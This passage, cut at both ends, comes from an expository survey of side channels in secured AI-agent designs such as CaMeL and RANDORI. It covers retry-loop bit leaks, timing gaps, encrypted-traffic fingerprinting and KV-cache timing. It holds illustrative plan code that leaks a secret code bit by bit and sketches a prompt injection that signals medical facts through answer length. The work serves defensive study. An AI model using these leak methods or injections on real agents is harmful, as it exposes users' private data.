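if (code // 2**k) % 2 == 1:
    send_email(to=outsider, body="x")
[][0]
```

The number k selects one binary digit of the code. If the digit is 1, the policy check refuses the email. If it is 0, the plan skips the email and fails on the last line, which tries to read the first item of an empty list. Either error leads to another attempt with a new k. If the privileged model can tell the two errors apart, each attempt reveals one bit. Ten attempts then reveal 10 bits, so two user requests are enough for the whole code.

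If the loop distinguishes m types of failure and allows n attempts, the number of possible outcomes is

N = 1 + m + m² + … + mⁿ.

The last term counts the cases in which every attempt fails, and each earlier term counts those in which the loop succeeds after a given number of failures. With one type of failure and ten attempts, the formula gives the 11 outcomes above. With four types, it gives 1,398,101, which is more than the number of six-digit codes. A loop could therefore reveal the whole code during one user request, even if it reported only which row of the earlier table each failure belonged to.

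These are upper limits, and particular observers may learn less. If the privileged model has to send the code out itself, it needs the tenth attempt to do so. With four types of failure, the nine earlier failures carry at most 18 bits, enough to narrow the code down to about four candidates. The operator of a tool that every attempt calls once at the start can only count attempts. The operator cannot tell whether the tenth attempt succeeded or failed, and so can distinguish only ten outcomes, or about 3.3 bits.

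### What censoring removes

According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's designers acknowledge that each attempt depends on earlier errors but doesn't carry those errors' labels. The designers try to reduce the effect by censoring the error messages, but Garby and colleagues judge that this provides no formal guarantee.

Even so, removing the text of a message makes a large difference. When Python fails to convert text into a number, its error message includes the text. If a plan tries to convert "483920 is your code" into a number, the uncensored message hands the whole code to the privileged model in a single attempt. If the text came from an attacker, the same message puts his words in front of the model that writes the plans. Censoring the text prevents both, but the privileged model may still receive other details:

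| What the loop passes to the privileged model | Most that ten attempts can reveal |
|---|---|
| The full error message | Whatever text the messages contain |
| One of four types of failure, and which of ten lines failed | About 53 bits |
| One of four types of failure | About 20.4 bits |
| One of two types of failure | About 11 bits |
| Only that the attempt failed | About 3.5 bits |

(The row for two types gives 11 bits instead of 10 because it also counts loops that end in a success.)

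A plan can encode data in the line numbers of its exceptions by failing at a different line for each value. Removing the line numbers makes failures harder to diagnose, however. A privileged model told only that its plan failed can't distinguish a misspelt name from an attempt to read the first item of an empty list, so it may need more attempts, and each of them can reveal a little more data.

Even under the strictest censoring, the privileged model can infer that a failure occurred when it is asked for another plan. Tool operators may also notice when a second attempt repeats the calls of the first.

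Failures can also influence the agent's actions. An attacker who controls only whether each attempt fails has far too few bits to spell out an instruction, but can keep making one approach fail until the privileged model tries another. This weakens CaMeL's control-flow integrity, because the replacement plan may contain steps that the first one lacked. The definition by Peters-Gill and colleagues, read strictly, excludes any plan written in response to an error that untrusted data caused.

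### What an attacker would need

The privileged model never reads the attacker's text, so the attacker cannot simply ask it for code that tests one bit at a time. Garby and colleagues infer the leak from how the retry loop works. The banking benchmark they ran CaMeL on tests whether the agent carries out an injected task, so it does not show how often the loop leaks secrets in practice.

An attacker could instead work through the quarantined model, provided it reads his email together with the secret code. His email could tell the model to return a malformed answer if the code's first digit is 5 or higher. That gives him one bit, but getting more bits from retries is harder. If the model starts each attempt with no memory of the last, it will read the same email, receive much the same question and probably fail in the same way, which reveals nothing new.

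The attacker can learn a new bit from each attempt only if something changes between attempts. An earlier attempt might leave a message in the mailbox, and the attacker could use the injection to tell the model to count such messages and move on to the next binary digit. The attacker could also send a series of emails, using each to ask about a different digit, and wait for the user to make more requests.

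The attacker must also be able to observe the result. If the plan opens a page on his website after the quarantined model answers, his server's log shows whether the run got that far. He sees nothing if the plan contacts only the user's bank. The privileged model may receive notice that the attempt failed, but it would not normally pass this on to him.

An attacker who controlled a privileged model would avoid most of these obstacles, because they could have it write the leaking code. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested injected instructions against systems of several CaMeL agents, using 949 attack cases for each of five models. The attacks succeeded in 0.5 per cent of cases with GPT-4.1, in 0.4 per cent with Gemini 2.5 Pro, and in none with the other three models. Every successful attack reached a privileged model by the same route as in their job-applicant example. The researchers had again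 turned off the policy checks, so these attacks did not need the retry loop. With the checks on, an attacker who reached a privileged model could use the loop to bypass them.

Failures can also leak information without an attacker. Suppose an agent pays a loan instalment each month and then posts "Paperwork done" in a group chat. If the bank rejects the payment, the run stops and the post never appears. Anyone in the chat who knows the routine can guess that the account was short of money. Nobody chose which fact would leak, and retrying does not extract a new bit each time, but the presence or absence of the post reveals something about the account every month.

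## Making failures reveal less

In the loan example, the missing post reveals that a payment was rejected because the plan stops at the error. If the plan carried on, the chat would show the same post every month.

### Errors as labelled values

Tallam and Miller propose replacing exceptions with a result type, similar to the results that LIO's blocks return. The plan then continues whether a step succeeds or fails. The loan plan starts out as two lines:

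```
receipt = pay_instalment()
post_to_chat("Paperwork done")
```

With a result type, it becomes:

```
result = pay_instalment()     # Ok(receipt) or Error(reason)
post_to_chat("Paperwork done")
tell_user(result)
```

The interpreter labels `result` secret whether it holds a receipt or an error, because either one shows whether the account had enough money. The plan has not branched on anything secret, so the program's position stays public and the policy check permits the post. The last line can show the user what happened because the user is allowed to read `result`.

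The post is now false in some months. To correct that, the plan would have to look at the result first:

```
if result.is_ok: post_to_chat("Paperwork done")
```

The post now depends on a secret condition, so the policy check blocks it and stops the run whenever the payment succeeded. The outcome of the payment again determines whether the run finishes.

Many plans also need the value inside the result. RANDORI, the agent Garby and colleagues built in their own language, has a function for this called `bind`, which takes a result and a next step. If the result holds a value, `bind` runs the step on it, and if it holds an error, `bind` skips the step and passes the error on. A plan can use `bind` to take the reference number from the receipt and save it in the user's private notes. But if the next step contacts an outside service, a missing request reveals the error. The interpreter therefore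 has to treat the step as a branch on the result and refuse any call in it that an outsider can see.

Result types help only with failures that the software is written to return as values. RANDORI's library handles a missing field in a record, for example, but Garby and colleagues say many other run-time errors still stop the program. Timing can also reveal an error, since a rejected payment may return sooner than a successful one and make the chat post appear earlier. Tallam and Miller propose making both cases take the same time, but they have tested neither proposal.

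Refusals by the interpreter are harder to turn into values than other failures. Under the no-sensitive-upgrade rule, the interpreter stops a plan that assigns to the public variable `urgent` inside a branch on the bank balance. If the plan could catch the resulting error and continue in a public context, that would reveal that the branch had run. The plan could then test other digits of the balance in the same way, so the rule would no longer limit the leak to one bit. For this reason, Garby and colleagues say that ordinary exception handling cannot soundly catch these errors.

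The language lets a program test a value's label before it acts. The program names a limit, and the test returns True if the value's label is within it. The result carries the limit's label. In one example, a program tests a value against the limit "secret" and returns the word "accepted", which is then labelled secret. The test avoids stopping the program, but everything the program does because of the result is restricted. The language also has an assertion, which leaves the label of the program's current position unchanged and stops the run if the value's label is over the limit. A programmer has to choose between restricting the later code and accepting that a stop may reveal one bit.

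### Running each plan only once

An agent can also stop after the first failure. The privileged model then receives no report of the failure, so it cannot write that information into another plan. A single attempt that either succeeds or fails can reveal only one bit, so an attacker trying to steal the six-digit code would need at least 20 user requests, compared with six for the most strictly censored loop of ten attempts.

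Without retries, every task whose first plan has a bug fails. Suppose a model writes a working plan 70 per cent of the time and its attempts succeed or fail independently. About 3 in 100 tasks would fail if the model had three attempts, compared with 30 in 100 if it had only one.

A privileged model is particularly likely to make mistakes on its first attempt because it has to write code for tool output it will never see. An ordinary agent can look at the output before deciding how to read it. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that the tool descriptions in AgentDojo, and in a benchmark of professional tasks called AssetOpsBench, did not specify the output format. They had to add the format to every description before CaMeL agents could perform reasonably well. This only has to be done once for each tool, but a plan can still fail if an outside service changes its format.

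Even with the added descriptions, CaMeL agents completed fewer AssetOpsBench tasks than unprotected agents, by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models and 13.4 points for the two strongest. Peters-Gill and colleagues also tested multi-CaMeL, their protocol for keeping tool output out of the instructions that one agent gives another, which lowered the completion rate by a further 3.2 points on average. These figures reflect all of CaMeL's restrictions together, so they do not isolate the effect of banning retries. They suggest that stronger models are better at planning without seeing tool output.

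Stopping after a failure can also leave a job half done. If a plan pays one bill and fails on the second, the user has to find out which payment went through before asking again. Each new request gives an outside observer another chance to learn something, although people repeat requests far less often than programs do.

### Practising on invented data

RANDORI keeps the retries but moves them to a practice stage that uses no real data. The name is a Japanese martial arts term for free-style sparring. In the version that Garby and colleagues built for banking tasks, the agent works as follows:

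1. The privileged model writes a plan for the user's request.
2. The interpreter runs the plan on an invented bank account. Tools that would send money or change a password do nothing, and the tool for reading files always returns the same placeholder sentence.
3. If the plan fails, the agent adds the error to the prompt and asks for another plan.
4. Once a plan succeeds, or the attempts run out, the model writes a final version for the real account.
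5. The interpreter runs the final version on the real data.

An error during a practice run can depend only on the user's request, the plan and the invented account, not on the real balance or an attacker's email, so the agent can give the model the full error message. CaMeL has to censor its error messages because its failed runs have already used real data.

Practising a plan exposes only the bugs that the invented data triggers, and Garby and colleagues deliberately made that data sparse. A plan might look for a payment with the subject "Monthly rent", find it in the invented account, and then find nothing in the real one. The prompt for the final version warns the model about this and tells it to have the quarantined model pick out the right payment instead. The final version may therefore differ from the plan that worked during practice. The interpreter checks its syntax, but the agent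 does not practise it again, so it can contain a new bug.

Practice also misses policy refusals, because the interpreter does not raise them at that stage. Take this plan:

```
bill  = read_file("bill.txt")
payee = ask_quarantined("Which account should I pay?", bill)
if get_balance() > 10000:
    send_money(to=payee, amount=100)
rate = get_exchange_rate("EUR")
```

In the practice run, the placeholder text counts as trusted and `send_money` does nothing, so the plan succeeds whatever the invented balance is. In the real run, the file is untrusted, and so is the account number the quarantined model extracts from it. RANDORI's policy requires a trusted recipient for a payment, so the interpreter stops the run at `send_money` if the real balance is above 10,000. As with CaMeL, the missing exchange-rate request reveals one bit about the balance, but RANDORI does not respond with another plan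 that could reveal a second bit.

If `send_money` were outside the branch, the interpreter would refuse it in every real run. The user's task would still fail, but the refusal would reveal nothing about the balance.

Garby and colleagues write that RANDORI will not get "stuck" during a live run, which could otherwise lead it to repeat payments, but an appendix to their paper describes information-flow errors that appear only in the live run. The design prevents repeated payments because the agent never restarts a live run, but it does not guarantee that the run will finish. The appendix suggests simulating the labels during practice, so that the model can repair a plan like the one above before it touches real data. A simulation could still miss a refusal that depends on a real label, such as the guest list of a particular meeting.

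RANDORI can also avoid some refusals through endorsement, which lets a plan mark an untrusted value as trusted. In the plan above, endorsing `payee` would allow the payment. The privileged model decides to endorse the value before any outside data can influence that decision, but whoever wrote the file then chooses who gets the money. Endorsement changes only a value's trust level, so a plan cannot use it to make a secret public.

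### Checking a plan before it runs

Software can find some policy violations from the code alone. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) adds such a check to CaMeL. Its software turns the plan into a map of every order in which the steps could run. The map includes both sides of every branch, and at a loop it allows for another repetition or an exit each time. The software also records where each argument comes from. The program nuXmv then searches the map for any path that breaks a rule.

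The plan that sends Bob a reminder shows how this works. One rule might be

AG(call_send_email ⇒ recipient_trusted),

where A means "on every path" and G means "at every step". The rule therefore forbids the plan from ever sending an email to an untrusted recipient. Bob's address comes from the quarantined model, so the software marks it as tainted, and the rule fails at the last step. nuXmv returns the path that led there, and CaMeLoT describes it to the privileged model, which rewrites the plan. All this happens before the interpreter fetches any email, so the feedback contains nothing from the mailbox and the model can try again without a leak.

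The rules can also cover the order of steps, or require a step to happen eventually. Nikolaou and colleagues tested seven such rules on an agent that handles security alerts. One required human approval before the agent cut a computer off from the network, and another required it to resolve or escalate every ticket it opened. CaMeLoT caught all seven deliberately broken plans, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The researchers had chosen most of the rules because CaMeL's policies cannot easily express them.

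CaMeLoT prevents some run-time refusals. It could reject the plan that pays a bill only when the balance is high, because it can check the payment without knowing the balance, and this would remove the leak to the exchange-rate service. But it fully covers only 22 of the 28 AgentDojo policies that CaMeL enforces, because the other six need information available only during a run. CaMeLoT also leaves CaMeL to enforce almost all restrictions on who may read a value. It would therefore let through the plan that sends Bob a summary of a meeting, and Bob could still learn from a refusal during the run that he was not invited.

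Nikolaou and colleagues compared the two systems on 97 AgentDojo tasks without attacks, with plan repair switched off in almost all cases. Both systems blocked the plan in 17 tasks, so the early check could have avoided a run that was going to fail. In nine tasks only CaMeLoT passed the plan, and in seven only CaMeL did. The researchers attribute most of these disagreements to CaMeL blocking plans because of information available only at run time.

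Checking early also rejects some safe plans, because the software treats a value as tainted if it cannot determine in advance whether the value is trustworthy. If Bob's address turned out to be one that the user already trusts, CaMeL might allow the email, but CaMeLoT would already have rejected the plan. A plan that passes can still fail because of a tool error or a malformed answer. The map has no path for either, since each ordinary step leads only to the next.

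Garby and colleagues describe two other systems that use a programming language's type checker to reject unsafe code before it runs. Tacit, from *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky and colleagues, 2026), uses Scala 3's type system to stop generated code from sending classified data over the network without permission. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026), the model writes code that must fit the types in the developer's program, so the same policies apply to the model's code and the developer's. The Haskell version is called TypeGuard.

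Both systems let the model read untrusted data and then write more code, so a type error can depend on that data even though the rejected code never runs. For example, an attacker's web page could lead the model to write code that fails the check. If the model has also read a secret, the failure could depend on the secret. Errors in RANDORI's practice stage and in CaMeLoT do not have this problem, because the model has seen no outside data when it writes the plan.

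Type checking does not rule out run-time refusals either. TypeGuard enforces its information-flow policies through LIO, the Haskell library described earlier, which can refuse an operation at run time. Garby and colleagues suggest using types to check the code in advance and their own label tracking for whatever remains.

In AgentDojo tests, TypeGuard resisted all 105 attacks in the Slack suite, and Tacit resisted attack in all but one of 1,926 trials across four suites. In the remaining trial, the benchmark's text matching counted a verbatim quotation as a successful attack. These scores do not measure how much a type error or a stopped run reveals.

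### Full storage

A limit on storage can also cause failures that depend on untrusted data. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that keeps a memory between sessions. Its protected model chooses the agent's actions, much like a privileged model. When the protected model requests an untrusted memory, it receives a reference instead of the text. It can read the text only after the user, or another language model acting as a checker, has confirmed that exact text on a screen.

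Jiang and colleagues prove a property they call reasoning integrity. It concerns two runs with the same user input and random choices but different untrusted data. If the confirmation screens and the decisions made on them are also the same in both runs, the protected model behaves identically.

A visible "memory full" error could break this property. Suppose an agent saves web pages as it reads them, and an attacker makes one page so long that it fills the memory and the next save fails. If the protected model receives the error, it may choose a different action. The attacker would then have influenced the agent through the page's length alone, even though nobody has confirmed any of the attacker's text.

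To keep the guarantee with limited storage, the software would have to make room silently. It could delete the oldest untrusted memory and report that the new one had been saved. It could not delete a trusted memory, because the protected model can read trusted memories and might notice that one was missing. Later searches would also have to return references without revealing the deletion.

The agent would then lose information without detecting the loss, and an attacker could push out useful memories by flooding the agent with text. The software could still warn the user, as long as the warning did not reach the protected model.

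### What policy enforcement cost in the banking tests

Garby and colleagues compared RANDORI with CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking suite. It has 16 tasks, and each agent attempted every task three times, for a total of 48 runs without attacks. The table shows how many runs completed the task:

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policy checks off | 32 | not tested | 34 |
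| CaMeL, policy checks on | 18 | not tested | 18 |
| RANDORI | 36 | 36 | 31 |
| RANDORI without endorsement | not reported | 30 | 26 |

Turning on the policy checks roughly halved the number of tasks that CaMeL completed. The estimates are imprecise because there were only 16 different tasks, and the 95 per cent confidence interval for CaMeL's completion rate with the checks on runs from about 11 to 64 per cent. The fall was clearer when the tasks included attacks. With GPT-5.2, CaMeL completed 71 per cent of tasks with the checks off and 30 per cent with them on, although these figures exclude the many runs that did not finish.

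TypeGuard's results on the Slack suite fell similarly, from 15 of 21 tasks completed to 8, when its policies were turned on. CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions. Zhou and colleagues observe that many of the tasks "involve flows that no secure policy would admit" and suggest asking the user to confirm in those cases.

RANDORI completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL did with its checks on, but RANDORI implements only some of CaMeL's policies. When it schedules a payment, for example, it requires the amount to be trusted but not the recipient. It can also use endorsement, which three of the banking tasks need because they ask the agent to act on the contents of a file. However, RANDORI's models had to write in a language they had never seen, while CaMeL's wrote Python.

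RANDORI resisted the attack in all but 2 of 1,296 runs. Two-thirds of those runs were easy to defend, because the attack needed a tool call or a file that a plan for the user's task would never include. The other 423 runs tested the policies better, and both successful attacks were among them. Both involved the same task, in which the user asks the agent to pay a bill described in a file. The attacker replaced the contents of the file, and the agent endorsed the new payment details. Without endorsement, the policy check blocks this attack, but it also blocks the legitimate payment.

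The benchmark leaves little room for policy checks to improve security, because CaMeL let only 5 attacks through in 622 completed runs with its checks off. With the checks on, it let none through in 588.

These results measure the effect of policy enforcement as a whole, not the effect of closing side channels. CaMeL used its ordinary retry loop both with and without policy checks, so the fall from 32 or 34 completed runs to 18 does not measure the effect of securing that loop. The comparison with RANDORI does not isolate the effect of practice either, because the two agents also differ in their language, prompts and policies. Garby and colleagues did not test RANDORI without its practice stage or measure how much an observer could learn from the failed runs.

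## Leaks through elapsed time

A plan can succeed in every run, make the same tool calls in the same order, and still leak a secret if the time between two calls depends on private data. Returning errors as values or practising on invented data doesn't prevent this leak, because it can happen even when nothing fails.

### Clocks inside the plan and clocks outside it

If a plan has a clock function, it can time its own work:

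```
start = now()
ask_quarantined("Summarise these letters", medical_letters)
seconds = now() - start
post_to_public_page(seconds)
```

The letters are secret, but the plan throws the summary away and publishes only a duration. Both clock readings come from a public source, so an interpreter that labels values by their origin would label `seconds` public, and the policy check would permit the post. Anyone who reads the page can then estimate the summary's length from the duration.

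A plan can measure elapsed time without a clock function. Web servers usually include the current time in their replies, so the plan could fetch a public page before and after the summary and subtract the times. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026), which compares agents with operating systems, points out that the current date reaches an agent as text, in its standing instructions or in a tool result. When a tool returned a forged time, the agent accepted it in all 15 test runs. Software that controls tool results can therefore hide the real time from an agent. The memory system by Jiang and colleagues stores a clock reading as untrusted data, like any other tool output, and keeps it from the protected model.

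Tallam and Miller propose taking precise timers away from untrusted code, or adding random error to the timers' readings. If the interpreter can run tasks in parallel, it would also have to hide the order in which they finish. Suppose one task reads the letters while another does a fixed amount of work, and each adds its name to a public list when it finishes. The order of the names reveals whether reading the letters took longer than the fixed work. *PhotoFinish* (2026) describes a similar trick in attacks on processors, where one thread counts steadily while another does the work, and the count serves as a clock.

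None of these measures affects an observer who has their own clock. The operator of a web server can time the requests that reach it even if the plan cannot access the time. Jiang and colleagues make the same distinction in their analysis, which covers a clock that the agent consults through a tool but not a delay that an outsider measures.

### Two harmless requests

Suppose the operator of an exchange-rate service wants to learn something about a user's medical letters. The user's agent runs this plan:

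```
fetch("https://rates.example/EUR")
summary = ask_quarantined("Summarise these letters", medical_letters)
fetch("https://rates.example/USD")
save_private_note(summary)
```

Both web addresses are public constants and the plan has no branches, so both requests pass the policy check. They reach the service in the same order whatever the letters contain. But the system can't send the second request until the quarantined model has finished the summary, so the time between the requests depends on the letters.

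A language model writes its answer one token at a time, where a token is a word or part of a word. For example, at 50 tokens a second, a 40-token summary takes 0.8 seconds and a 400-token summary takes 8 seconds. If the operator can distinguish thirty gaps, each run reveals at most log₂ 30 bits, or about 4.9. Thirty evenly spaced gaps between 0.8 and 8 seconds would be about a quarter of a second apart, or the time the model takes to write twelve tokens. Leaking the six-digit code from the retry example would then take at least five runs, because four runs can distinguish only 810,000 of the million possible codes.

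A summary written without an injection would reveal much less than this limit. The summary's length depends on many facts at once, so the operator might infer only that the user has a long medical file. An attacker could make the channel far more useful by injecting an instruction into one of the letters, such as one telling the quarantined model to write 400 tokens if any letter mentions cancer and 40 if none does. The attacker would also have to run the rate service or get its timings from someone who does.

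For models used alone, *Time Will Tell* (2024) reports a strong correlation between execution time, the number of tokens a model writes, and sensitive attributes of its input. In experiments, an attacker could infer the target language of a translation or the result of a classification from timing and text lengths.

*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) describes the published attack closest to the two-request example. A hostile web server tries to find out which of four private subtasks a visiting agent is working on. The server's page offers material for each subtask after a different delay. Once the agent has what it needs, it requests a "continue" address that is the same for every subtask, and the server infers the subtask from the time since the page loaded. Identifying one of four equally likely subtasks reveals two bits. The server creates the delays in this attack, whereas the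 private data creates them in the rate example. The attack also relies on the agent reading the page to decide what it needs, and a privileged model never sees the page.

### What else changes the gap

The length of an answer is only one of the things that can alter the gap. A branch can do it too:

```
fetch("https://rates.example/EUR")
if balance > 10000:
    advice = ask_quarantined("Suggest a savings account", statement)
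fetch("https://rates.example/USD")
```

The branch makes no call that the operator can see, so the policy check doesn't stop it. If the balance is high, the second request arrives several seconds later. The program-counter label doesn't prevent this delay.

When an agent loops over private items, the gap grows in proportion to their number. Tallam and Miller put GPT-4's latency at one to two seconds per request, and estimate that a quarantined model could take more than ten seconds to read ten emails one by one. If the operator knows that each email takes about two seconds, a gap of 24 seconds suggests twelve emails. Blocking state-changing calls inside the loop would not prevent this leak, because the loop makes no such calls.

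Many models also write out hidden reasoning before they answer. A model asked whether a letter mentions a hospital might produce 100 tokens of reasoning if the letter is clear and 2,000 if it is ambiguous. At 50 tokens a second, that takes 2 seconds or 40, although the answer is a single word either way. A quarantined model restricted to yes or no can pass only one bit to the plan, but the operator may learn more than that from the delay.

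Generation speed can also depend on the text. In speculative decoding, a small model proposes the next few tokens and a large model checks them together, so predictable text comes out faster than surprising text of the same length.

Retries give more information to an observer who can measure elapsed time. If the quarantined model returns a malformed answer and the software asks again, the gap between requests grows by the time the second attempt takes. If the whole run starts over, the operator sees the first request repeated after a pause that includes the time the privileged model took to write a new plan. He may also learn roughly where each attempt failed, because a plan that stops at an early line restarts sooner.

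Parallel calls can make the gap less informative. Three summaries that take 2, 3 and 8 seconds delay the second request by 13 seconds if the interpreter runs them one after another, but by only 8 if it runs them in parallel. In the parallel case, the operator learns only that the slowest summary took 8 seconds, not how long the other two took. But parallel calls may slow each other down, in which case the shorter ones affect the gap again.

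The step at which a call happens can leak a secret even to an observer who can't measure elapsed time. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) gives an example in which a user approves one exact tool call, which is secret and which the agent may make only once. An attacker injects a call, and the software refuses it unless it matches the approved one. If it matches, it goes through one step early, and the software later refuses the plan's own call. An observer who sees only the order of requests can't tell whether the attacker guessed the approved call, but one who also sees the step at which the call happened can.

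### Noise and averaging

The gap between two requests varies from run to run even when the private data stays the same, because network traffic and the load on model servers change, and a model may phrase the same summary in different ways. A half-second difference is easy to see if the gap normally varies by a tenth of a second, but hard to see if it varies by several seconds.

Researchers therefore divide the difference by the spread. *Characterizing Contention-Induced Reliability Collapse in KV-Cache Timing Side Channels* (2026) measures how well an attacker can separate slow responses from fast ones as

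d = (average slow time − average fast time) / s,

where s is the typical variation within each group. If d is near zero, the two groups overlap so much that a single measurement is almost useless.

An attacker who can measure many times can average the results. The random error in an average of n independent measurements is √n times smaller than the error in one. For example, a secret might have two equally likely values, with an average gap half a second longer for one than for the other. If the noise is normally distributed with a standard deviation of one second, an attacker who guesses from a single run is wrong about 40 per cent of the time. Averaging 16 runs reduces the error rate to 16 per cent, and averaging 100 reduces it to 0.6 per cent. If the difference were half as large, the attacker would need four times as many runs for the same accuracy.

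The secret has to stay the same over all those runs, and somebody has to start them. The operator of the rate service can't make the user's agent summarise the letters again. If the agent summarises them once a day, 100 measurements take more than three months, by which time there may be new letters. An attacker who can trigger runs, for example by sending emails to an agent that handles each one automatically, is in a much better position.

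*PhotoFinish* notes that averaging also can't recover a difference between two times if a coarse clock always rounds them to the same value. Suppose a server's log records only whole seconds. If the first request always arrives exactly on the second, gaps of 8.1 and 8.4 seconds both appear in the log as 8, however often the operator measures them. But if the first request arrives at a random moment, the shorter gap appears as 9 in one run in ten and the longer gap in four runs in ten. The averages are then 8.1 and 8.4, so the random arrival times let the operator recover the difference. If the arrival time doesn't vary, an attacker can try to enlarge the difference until it exceeds the clock's resolution, for instance by getting the agent to process a hundred messages instead of one.

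### An eavesdropper on the network

A network eavesdropper can watch the exchanges between the agent and its model directly, so he doesn't need two requests to the same service. TLS, the usual encryption for web traffic, hides the text but leaves the size and timing of each message visible. Many model services also stream their answers, sending each token or small group of tokens as soon as it is ready, so the eavesdropper sees a long series of sizes and intervals.

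In *Whisper Leak*, McDonald and Bar Or (2025) tested how much this series reveals about a user's question. They wrote 100 versions of a question about one sensitive topic, the legality of money laundering, and put each version to 28 commercial models up to 100 times. They also put 11,716 unrelated questions from Quora to the models. They then trained three kinds of classifier to recognise the topic from packet sizes, the intervals between packets, or both, and tested them on versions of the question held back from training.

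McDonald and Bar Or measure accuracy by the area under the precision-recall curve (AUPRC). Precision is the share of flagged conversations that concern the topic, and recall is the share of conversations on the topic that the classifier flags. A stricter classifier usually gains precision and loses recall. AUPRC summarises this trade-off in a single number, with 100 per cent for a perfect classifier. They put random guessing at 50 per cent in their tests.

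With the best classifier for each model, 17 of the 28 models scored above 97 per cent. McDonald and Bar Or give the threshold as 98 per cent in their text, but only 13 models reach that in their table. Most of the information came from sizes. On average, classifiers scored between 93 and 97 per cent using only sizes, depending on the type of classifier, and about 70 per cent using only timing. For Mistral Large, they scored 100 per cent with sizes alone and at most 64 per cent with timing alone.

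Google's three models were exceptions, with a higher best score from timing alone than from sizes alone (83 per cent compared with 79 for Gemini 2.5 Pro). They send many tokens in each message, from about 18 for Gemini 2.5 Pro to more than 50 for the two Gemini 1.5 models, and this hides the lengths of individual words.

Very few conversations in real traffic would concern the chosen topic, so McDonald and Bar Or estimated precision for a case with 10,000 other conversations for each one about money laundering. For 17 models, they projected 100 per cent precision while catching a fifth of the target conversations. This projection is fragile because it rests on the classifier flagging none of the unrelated questions in the test set, which their results imply numbered about 2,340. A single false alarm among those questions would correspond to more than four for every target conversation in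 the projected traffic, and precision would drop to about 4.5 per cent. McDonald and Bar Or advise a conservative reading.

The researchers began notifying providers in June 2025 and published in November, after some had responded. OpenAI and xAI introduced defences in August, Mistral in September and Microsoft in October. Other providers declined or never replied. OpenAI and Microsoft add text of random length to each message, which hides message sizes but doesn't directly hide timing. All the measurements date from before these changes, so they don't show how well the attack works today.

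An agent may leak less than a chat because its interpreter needs the complete answer before it can run the next line, so streaming has little benefit. If the agent requests the answer in one piece, the eavesdropper sees only the total size and total wait. But one task may give the eavesdropper dozens of such exchanges to observe.

### Recognising agents and tasks by their traffic

Tools add their own delays and affect message sizes. Zhang, Deng and colleagues (2025), in *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis*, recorded encrypted traffic between users and agent services. When an agent drew a diagram through a slow outside service, a short burst of text was followed by a long silence. A literature search through a fast service produced a steady stream of data almost at once. Image generation produced some text, a wait and then a large burst of data.

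The AgentPrint attack cuts the traffic into short time slices and counts the packets and bytes in each. A neural network then learns the patterns in these counts. It distinguished five kinds of agent behaviour with an F1 score of 0.924 and 50 individual agents with a score of 0.866. The F1 score combines precision and recall, and a perfect classifier scores 1. When the tests included agents that were not in the training data, the median score for identifying an agent stayed above 0.80.

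Zhang and colleagues also tested whether the mix of agents a person uses reveals their occupation. They sorted occupations into 12 groups and counted a guess as correct if the right group was among the top three, which would happen a quarter of the time by chance. The attack succeeded for 73.9 per cent of simulated users in occupations where people are likely to use language models, and for 58.9 per cent across all occupations. For 49 real participants, the figure was 69.1 per cent, based on which agents they preferred.

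An observer may also be able to identify the kind of task. In *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026) had teams of two to five agents work on tasks from ten categories, including contract analysis, bug fixing and medical questions. A classifier then identified the category from the encrypted traffic between the agents and their models. It was right about 85 per cent of the time, compared with 10 per cent for guessing.

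They then removed every feature based on packet sizes or the amount of data, leaving features such as timing, idle periods, direction and the number of packets in a burst. The classifier was still right 54 per cent of the time when the agents talked to each other directly, and 59 per cent when a central planner coordinated them. Making all messages the same size would therefore leave a considerable leak. With all the features included, an observer who could see only one agent's traffic identified the task in 66.5 per cent of cases when the agents talked directly, and 78 per cent when they used a central planner.

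These conditions favoured the attacker. Every task belonged to one of ten categories that the classifier had been trained on, and the observer knew when each run began and ended. The agents all used the same small model on a local machine, and Pouryousef and colleagues recorded the traffic there, so it included no delays from a real network. The classifier also did worse when the agents worked together differently. When it was trained on teams with one structure and tested on teams with the other, its accuracy fell from 83 to 52 per cent.

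Running the model locally hides its traffic from an outside eavesdropper, but the agent's tool calls still cross the network. In *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents*, Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues (2025) studied agents that investigate a question by visiting 70 to 140 websites in a short time. An internet provider can see which sites the agent visits and when, though not which pages it reads. Jeong and colleagues had a language model reconstruct the user's question from this record. By their own measure of similarity, it recovered over 73 per cent of the question's purpose and subject. From several sessions by the same person, it also inferred up to 19 of 32 personal traits. The attack still worked when the observer could see only 60 per cent of the sites.

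Much of that leak comes from the choice of sites rather than the timing. For CaMeL and FIDES, this part of the leak resembles the earlier example of a planner that reads a medical file and then picks one of sixteen public links. The attack assumes the user has no VPN or similar service to hide the addresses.

An attacker can also make the traffic easier to read. *SkillWatermark* (2026) describes an attack through skills, which are packages of instructions that users add to their agents. The attacker's skill contains phrases that control how much text the agent writes, and so the size of the bursts that an eavesdropper sees. The attacker can assign different sizes to different kinds of user and infer a user's traits from the encrypted traffic. This makes answer length a covert channel, as the injection in the medical letters did. Longer answers also take longer to write, so an operator who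 can see only the elapsed time might be able to receive the same signal.

Traffic analysis takes considerable effort in practice. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026), which considers it as a way for companies to find unauthorised agents, notes that the observer needs a recording point on the network path and a trained classifier for each agent and provider. The result is only a probability and doesn't identify the user or program responsible.

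### Another customer of the same model server

Someone who cannot see the agent's traffic may still learn part of its prompts by timing their own requests to the same model server. This is possible when the server reuses work from one customer's prompt to answer another customer faster.

Before a model writes the first token of its answer, it must process the entire prompt. For each token of the prompt, it computes sets of numbers called keys and values, which it uses when processing later tokens. A token's keys and values depend only on that token and the ones before it. If two prompts begin with the same 1,000 tokens, the keys and values for those tokens are the same in both, so the server can store them after the first prompt and reuse them for the second. This is called prefix caching, and the store is known as a KV cache. When the beginning of a request is already in the cache (a cache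 hit), the server skips much of the processing and the first token arrives sooner. *Mirage* (Yan and Zhang, 2026) reports that prefix caching often reduces latency by as much as 73 per cent.

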